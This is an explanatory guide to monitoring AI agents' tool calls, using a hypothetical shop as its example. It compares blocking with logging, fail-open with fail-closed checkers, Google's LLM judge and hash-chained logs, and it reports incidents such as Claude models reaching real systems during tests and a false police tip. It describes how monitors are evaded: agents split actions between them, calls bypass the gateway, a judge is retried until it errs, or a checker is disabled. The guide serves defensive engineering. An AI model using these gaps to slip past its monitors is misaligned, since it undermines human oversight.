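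Rules about the sequence of actions can fail in a similar way when the actions are split between agents. Suppose the shop forbids emails to outsiders after an agent has read an order. One agent reads order 1042 and passes the details to another, which emails them to a stranger. Each agent has its own monitor, and neither monitor records both the read and the email, so neither detects a violation. Ji and colleagues compare such agents to colluding Android apps, where an app that can read Gmail credentials but has no internet access passes them to an app that has it.

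To enforce the rule, the shop needs either one monitor that follows the whole task across agents, as SEAGENT does, or labels sent with each message. Enforcing it may block harmless actions more often. For example, once the emailing agent has received a message labelled as order data, the rule also stops it from asking a courier an unrelated question.

### Harm that the rules permit

Sometimes the policy allows the harmful action. An attacker can exploit this by imitating normal traces or steering the agent into a permitted branch, but a mistaken agent can cause the same harm without an attacker. Rashidi describes a benchmark of 500 scenarios that measures how often coding agents do more than the user requested. Claude Code did so in 0.0 percent of cases when the prompt stated what it was authorised to do, and in 17.1 percent when the researchers removed that statement. The agent had permission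 for the extra actions, so a permission check would not have blocked them.

Limits on arguments reduce the harm from each action, and caps reduce the total harm. If the shop allows refunds of up to £100 and sets no cap on the total, an agent that wrongly refunds 500 orders could pay out £50,000. A daily cap would limit the loss to, say, £1,000 a day. *Matoi* (2026) requires checking each effect and the remaining total budget. *Agenra* (2026) counts calls against a limit and saves the new count before the tool runs, so a call that takes effect is counted even if its reply is lost.

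A cap doesn't distinguish deserved refunds from undeserved ones. If an attacker uses up the day's £1,000, the monitor blocks Ana's legitimate refund until the next day. Caps also do little when a single action causes all the damage, as in the PocketOS deletion. Delays and human approval work better against such actions.

A human reviewer can use facts that the policy leaves out, but has to understand what the agent is proposing. The PocketOS request identified the volume only by a string of letters and digits, so someone who saw only the command could not have known that the volume held the production database. An approval screen should show the resource's ordinary name, its environment, and whether the action is reversible.

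Approval also takes time and attention. Lambert groups up to six similar requests on one screen and accepts that the assistant can't change anything in the background. The shop could require approval only for larger refunds, pay smaller ones automatically within the daily cap, and delay every deletion of customer records long enough for staff to cancel it.

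## Blocking an action compared with recording it

Two monitors can apply the same rule to Ana's second refund and get the same result, but only a monitor that holds the payment until the check is finished can stop it. The other just records the result in a log. Some products can do either, depending on one setting.

### Four arrangements

| Arrangement | When the decision falls | If the checker crashes or times out | Guarantee |
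|---|---|---|---|
| Logging, with a later review | Hours to months after the effect | The agent carries on, and the log may have gaps | None about the action, only evidence of it |
| Alerting during the run | While the agent works, often after the effect | The agent carries on, and nobody gets an alert | None about the flagged action, though a quick response can stop later ones |
| A model judges each call before it runs | Before the effect | Depends on a setting | No checked call runs without the judge's approval, but the judge can be wrong |
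| A fixed rule denies calls before they run | Before the effect | Depends on a setting | Every checked call that runs satisfies the written rule, if the monitor's facts are right |

The last two guarantees hold only if the software refuses calls when the checker gives no answer.

An alert comes sooner than a review but may still come too late. The PocketOS deletion took nine seconds, too little time for a person to read a message and respond. Alerts help more when harm builds up over many calls, as when an agent reads a hundred support tickets for an attacker. Alerts also help only if people act on them. According to Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), human reviewers sometimes dismissed automated warnings about flawed training tasks as false alarms, and the tasks stayed in use longer than they should have.

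A system can combine blocking actions with reviewing records of them. Anthropic had monitored some high-risk evaluations in real time, but for most it only ran automated reviews on a sample of transcripts afterwards. In summer 2026, after finding that Claude models had gained unauthorised access to real computer systems during security tests, it added a classifier that detects attempts to escape a test environment. When it flags an attempt, the classifier blocks the tool call before it runs, ends the task and alerts a person.

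### When the checker gives no answer

A system fails open if it lets a call run when the checker crashes or times out, and fails closed if it blocks the call. IBM's Bob can fail open when a hook crashes, while Agent-C fails closed when its solver times out.

If the system fails closed, the agent can't act while the checker is down. An operator can choose whether each tool fails open or closed. The shop might let a search of its public catalogue fail open, but refunds should fail closed, because paying Ana an hour late does less harm than paying her twice. Failing open is also riskier when the system is under attack, since an attacker could disable the checker by overloading it. Dang's threat model excludes attacks that overload Praetor's gateway.

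Logging can also fail closed, meaning the application refuses to run a call until it has stored a log entry for that call. This doesn't prevent a forbidden refund, but it ensures that every refund made through the application leaves a record.

### Google's judge model

Google's semantic governance policies use a language model to judge tool calls against rules that an operator writes in plain English. They were in preview in November 2026, as Pogorelec (2026), in *Google's semantic governance policies can block an AI agent's tool call*, reports. Google Cloud's *Semantic governance overview* describes how a check works:

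1. The agent's model replies with a proposed tool call.
2. A gateway between the model and the agent intercepts the reply and sends the call, the rules and the chat history to the judge.
3. The judge checks whether the call matches what the user asked for and whether it complies with the rules.
4. If either check fails, the gateway replaces the call with a denial message, so the agent's software never receives a call to run.

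In one of Google's examples, a rule forbids automated refunds above $75, and the judge rejects a refund of $89. A guard in a state machine can enforce this limit more reliably by comparing two numbers. The judge is more useful for rules about meaning. In an example from Pogorelec, a finance team's agent may send unreleased quarterly results only to company addresses. No automaton can determine from a call's text whether an email reveals those results. The shop's state machine had the same problem with order details, so it denied every email to a courier after `read_order`. A judge could allow a harmless question and block one that included Ana's delivery note.

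But the judge can be wrong. Deepti Sehrawat, a Google engineer quoted by Pogorelec, warns that verdicts "may vary" because they come from a language model. Suppose a judge wrongly allows a forbidden call 2 percent of the time. If its errors were independent, an agent that tried 20 times would have about a 33 percent chance (1 − 0.98²⁰) of getting the call through at least once. A real judge's errors on similar calls are probably not independent, so this figure only illustrates the risk.

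The judge can also use only the facts it is given. Sehrawat advises operators to include in the agent's instructions any fact that a policy depends on, such as the date of an earnings release. Another of Google's example rules allows shipping only to "addresses that have been previously validated". A state machine would save each validated address, while the judge has to find the validation in the chat history. The judge could miss the validation in a long conversation, or accept a false claim that an address was validated.

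Google Cloud presents the judge as an addition to fixed access controls. If a call must pass both, the fixed rules still block a refund they forbid, even if the judge approves it. The shop could enforce its refund limits with a state machine and use the judge to check the content of emails. The judge takes more computation to run. A sample log entry in Google Cloud's *Configure semantic governance policies* records 1,859 model tokens for checking one refund, while Praetor's fixed lookup added 2.2 milliseconds per call in Dang's tests.

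The setup instructions set `failOpen` to false, so the gateway should refuse a reply if the judge is unavailable. But a system that fails closed in this way can still let unchecked calls through, because the setting applies only to replies that the gateway sends to the judge. The gateway selects these by the URL path of the request to the model, and a request to a new model provider may not match. The judge also doesn't support streamed replies, which arrive piece by piece. Google Cloud lists both among the reasons an operator might find no verdict for a call.

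### Testing which arrangement a product has

The shop can use a test account at its payment service to check whether a monitor blocks a forbidden call. It refunds a test order once, requests a forbidden second refund, and then looks at the payment service's records. The agent's reply isn't good evidence, because an agent can report a refusal after the money has gone, or a payment that never happened. The first refund is a control. If neither refund appears in the records, the connection may be broken, so the missing second refund doesn't show that the monitor blocked it.

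The tester should send the second request directly to the point where the agent's calls enter the monitor. If the tester asks for it in the chat instead, the model may not propose the call, and the monitor won't be tested. If the product uses a judge, the tester also has to repeat the request in many wordings, since one refusal shows only that the judge can block it.

Next, the tester should stop the checker and send a permitted refund and a forbidden one. A system that fails closed refuses both, and one that fails open pays both. The tester should then restart the checker and delay its responses beyond the time limit, because software may handle a timeout differently from a crash.

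Finally, the tester should look for a setting that turns blocking off. Google's judge has a dry-run mode, which logs a verdict for every call but never blocks one, so the log can contain the verdict `DENY` for a refund that the shop has paid. Gloo, another software vendor, gives each policy an enforcement level. A policy whose action is "block" stops a matching call at the level "hard" but only logs it at the level "audit". Because changing one word in a configuration file can turn blocking off, the shop should repeat the first test after every update.

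### A false tip found after 72 days

In October 2026, Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) disclosed several kinds of unwanted behaviour by its Claude models, including submitting a sensitive form on a real website. ABC News' *Anthropic AI model made false tip in unsolved Philly murder* (2026) describes one case. Claude Haiku 4.5 was making up example tasks for randomly chosen web pages and carrying them out. On the Philadelphia police's page for unsolved murders, it filled in the tip form and wrote that it recalled seeing someone matching the description near the scene.

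The police gave ABC News these dates:

| Date in 2026 | Event | Days since the tip |
|---|---|---|
| 18 July | Claude submits the tip | 0 |
| 28 September | Anthropic discovers it, according to what it told the police | 72 |
| 7 October | Anthropic notifies the police | 81 |

The police called the delay unacceptable. Anthropic describes the real-world impact of the cases it has found as minimal. In this case, the police website had flagged the tip as spam, and it never reached the homicide investigators. If it had reached them, they could have spent almost twelve weeks on a false lead before anyone told them where the tip came from.

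A monitor that blocked violations of Claude's instructions might not have stopped the tip. According to Anthropic's report, as quoted by ABC News, the instructions banned logins, new accounts, purchases, entering personal data and destructive submissions, but not forms in general. A fixed rule with the same list would have permitted this form, and a judge would have had to decide whether a false tip counts as destructive. Denial by default would have worked better because it blocks every form that nobody has approved. Anthropic has since cut off live web access for its internal evaluations, according to *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests* (Southern, 2026). That also prevents harmful submissions that nobody thought to forbid, but it rules out tests that need real websites.

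### What logs do well

Investigators need logs because blocking a call doesn't show what led up to it, or what an agent did before anyone wrote the rule. The Next Web's *Anthropic scanned 481 million transcripts to find four models* describes Anthropic's search for models that had reached the open internet. The search traced all four incidents to evaluations built by the same outside partner, where a configuration error had connected the models to the internet.

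Logs also let outsiders hold an operator to account, but only if those outsiders can see them. In a September 2026 letter to Anthropic, the Office of Rep. Casar (2026) in the US Congress complained that the company had not released the logs of its security incidents as requested.

Developers can use logs to improve their rules. Google's judge records a reason with each verdict, which can help a developer find a rule that blocks legitimate calls. However, the reason is text from a language model and may not reflect what led to the verdict. A monitor cannot block some events, such as a customer's reply, and can only record them.

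Recording an action may be enough if the shop can undo it and somebody reads the log in time. Railway now delays deletions by 48 hours, so a customer who reviews the log daily can cancel a mistaken deletion, but a weekly review will usually be too late.

### Hash-chained logs

A log is weak evidence if the people it incriminates can edit it. A hash chain makes edits detectable. A hash function turns any text into a short fingerprint, and each entry's fingerprint also depends on the one before it:

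```
hᵢ = H(hᵢ₋₁, entryᵢ)
```

A toy version multiplies the previous fingerprint by 7, adds the amount of the refund and keeps the last two digits, starting from 1. Suppose somebody changes the second refund in the log from £60 to £6:

| Entry | Original amount | Original fingerprint | Edited amount | New fingerprint |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | £20 | 27 | £20 | 27 |
| 2 | £60 | 49 | £6 | 95 |
| 3 | £15 | 58 | £15 | 80 |

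The edit changes the fingerprints of the edited entry and the one after it. Two-digit fingerprints would be easy to forge, but with a real hash function nobody can feasibly find a different entry with the same fingerprint.

Someone who controls the whole log can edit an entry and recompute all the later fingerprints. They can also delete the newest entries, which leaves a shorter but valid chain. To detect such changes, the operator regularly publishes the latest fingerprint somewhere the editor can't change it. If an auditor has the original fingerprint, 58, a log that now ends in 80 must have changed. Dang's design for Praetor uses an append-only log of this general kind and publishes it to an external transparency log. An attacker who can overwrite files on the host machine could alter the log undetected before it is published.

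### Why an unaltered log can be incomplete

The chain proves that nobody has changed the entries since the operator published the fingerprint, but not that the software wrote an entry for every action. If the agent pays a refund by a route that avoids the monitor, the log has no entry for it and the fingerprints still match. Dang explicitly leaves such direct calls out of scope. Praetor's logging requirement also covers only blocked calls, so a log that meets it might omit a harmful call that Praetor allowed.

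An entry can also be wrong even if nobody has altered it, because the chain protects whatever the software wrote. In the double refund, the first entry would correctly record that no reply arrived, but a reader might conclude that the shop had not paid the refund.

To check that the log is complete, the shop needs a second record from a source the agent doesn't control. If the payment service's statement lists 42 refunds and the log has 41, one refund bypassed the log. An operator can compare the verdicts of Google's judge with the gateway's traffic records, which cover all the agent interactions that pass through the gateway, according to Google Cloud's *Govern your agents*. This comparison finds calls that reached the gateway without getting a verdict, but it can't find calls that avoided the gateway, because they appear in neither record.

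A search can miss incidents even when records of them exist. Anthropic first scanned about 141,000 transcripts of security tests and found three incidents. SecurityWeek reports that this scan missed a separate batch, which Anthropic came across in August while preparing material for an outside investigator. The batch contained a fourth break-in, from January.

### From recording to blocking

A new rule may block legitimate work, so Sehrawat recommends a dry run before enforcement. Gloo similarly has an intermediate level, "soft", for rules that operators are still testing. The shop could introduce its rules in four stages:

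| Stage | What the software does | What the shop measures before moving on |
|---|---|---|
| Record | Logs every call | Whether every refund on the payment service's statement has a log entry |
| Dry run | Also logs what the rules would have denied | How many known violations the rules catch, and how many legitimate calls they would deny |
| Partial blocking | Enforces the rules in a random share of conversations | Task completion and complaints, compared with the other conversations |
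| Full blocking | Enforces the rules everywhere | Wrong denials, unlogged refunds and the results of repeated enforcement tests |

The first measurement has to come before the others because they depend on the log. If a tenth of refunds leave no log entry, the dry run can't show how the rules would have treated those refunds.

The dry run needs enough legitimate calls to estimate how often the rules wrongly deny one. If staff check 300 legitimate calls and find no wrong denials, the true rate could still be as high as 1 percent, at 95 percent confidence. If each task makes ten calls and errors are independent, that rate would affect up to 1 − 0.99¹⁰, or 9.6 percent, of tasks. Checking 3,000 calls without finding an error would lower the limit to about 1 percent of tasks. The shop has to take known violations from test traces, such as the double refund and the leaked order, because real ones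 may be too rare to appear during the dry run.

A dry run never refuses an action, so it can't measure how the agent responds to a refusal. The agent might find a permitted way to finish the task, repeat the same call or tell Ana that the shop doesn't give refunds. Partial blocking tests this, and choosing the conversations at random makes the comparison fair. The shop should also deliberately stop the checker at this stage, while only some customers would notice the outage.

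During the first two stages, every violation still takes effect, so the shop shouldn't put all its rules through them at the same pace. The ban on a second refund has few legitimate exceptions and protects money that is hard to recover, so the shop can enforce it from the first day and send disputed cases to staff. A judge's rule about email content needs a longer dry run because its errors are harder to predict. If wrong denials rise after a tool changes, the shop can return that rule to dry run and have a person approve the calls it covered until the developer has fixed it.
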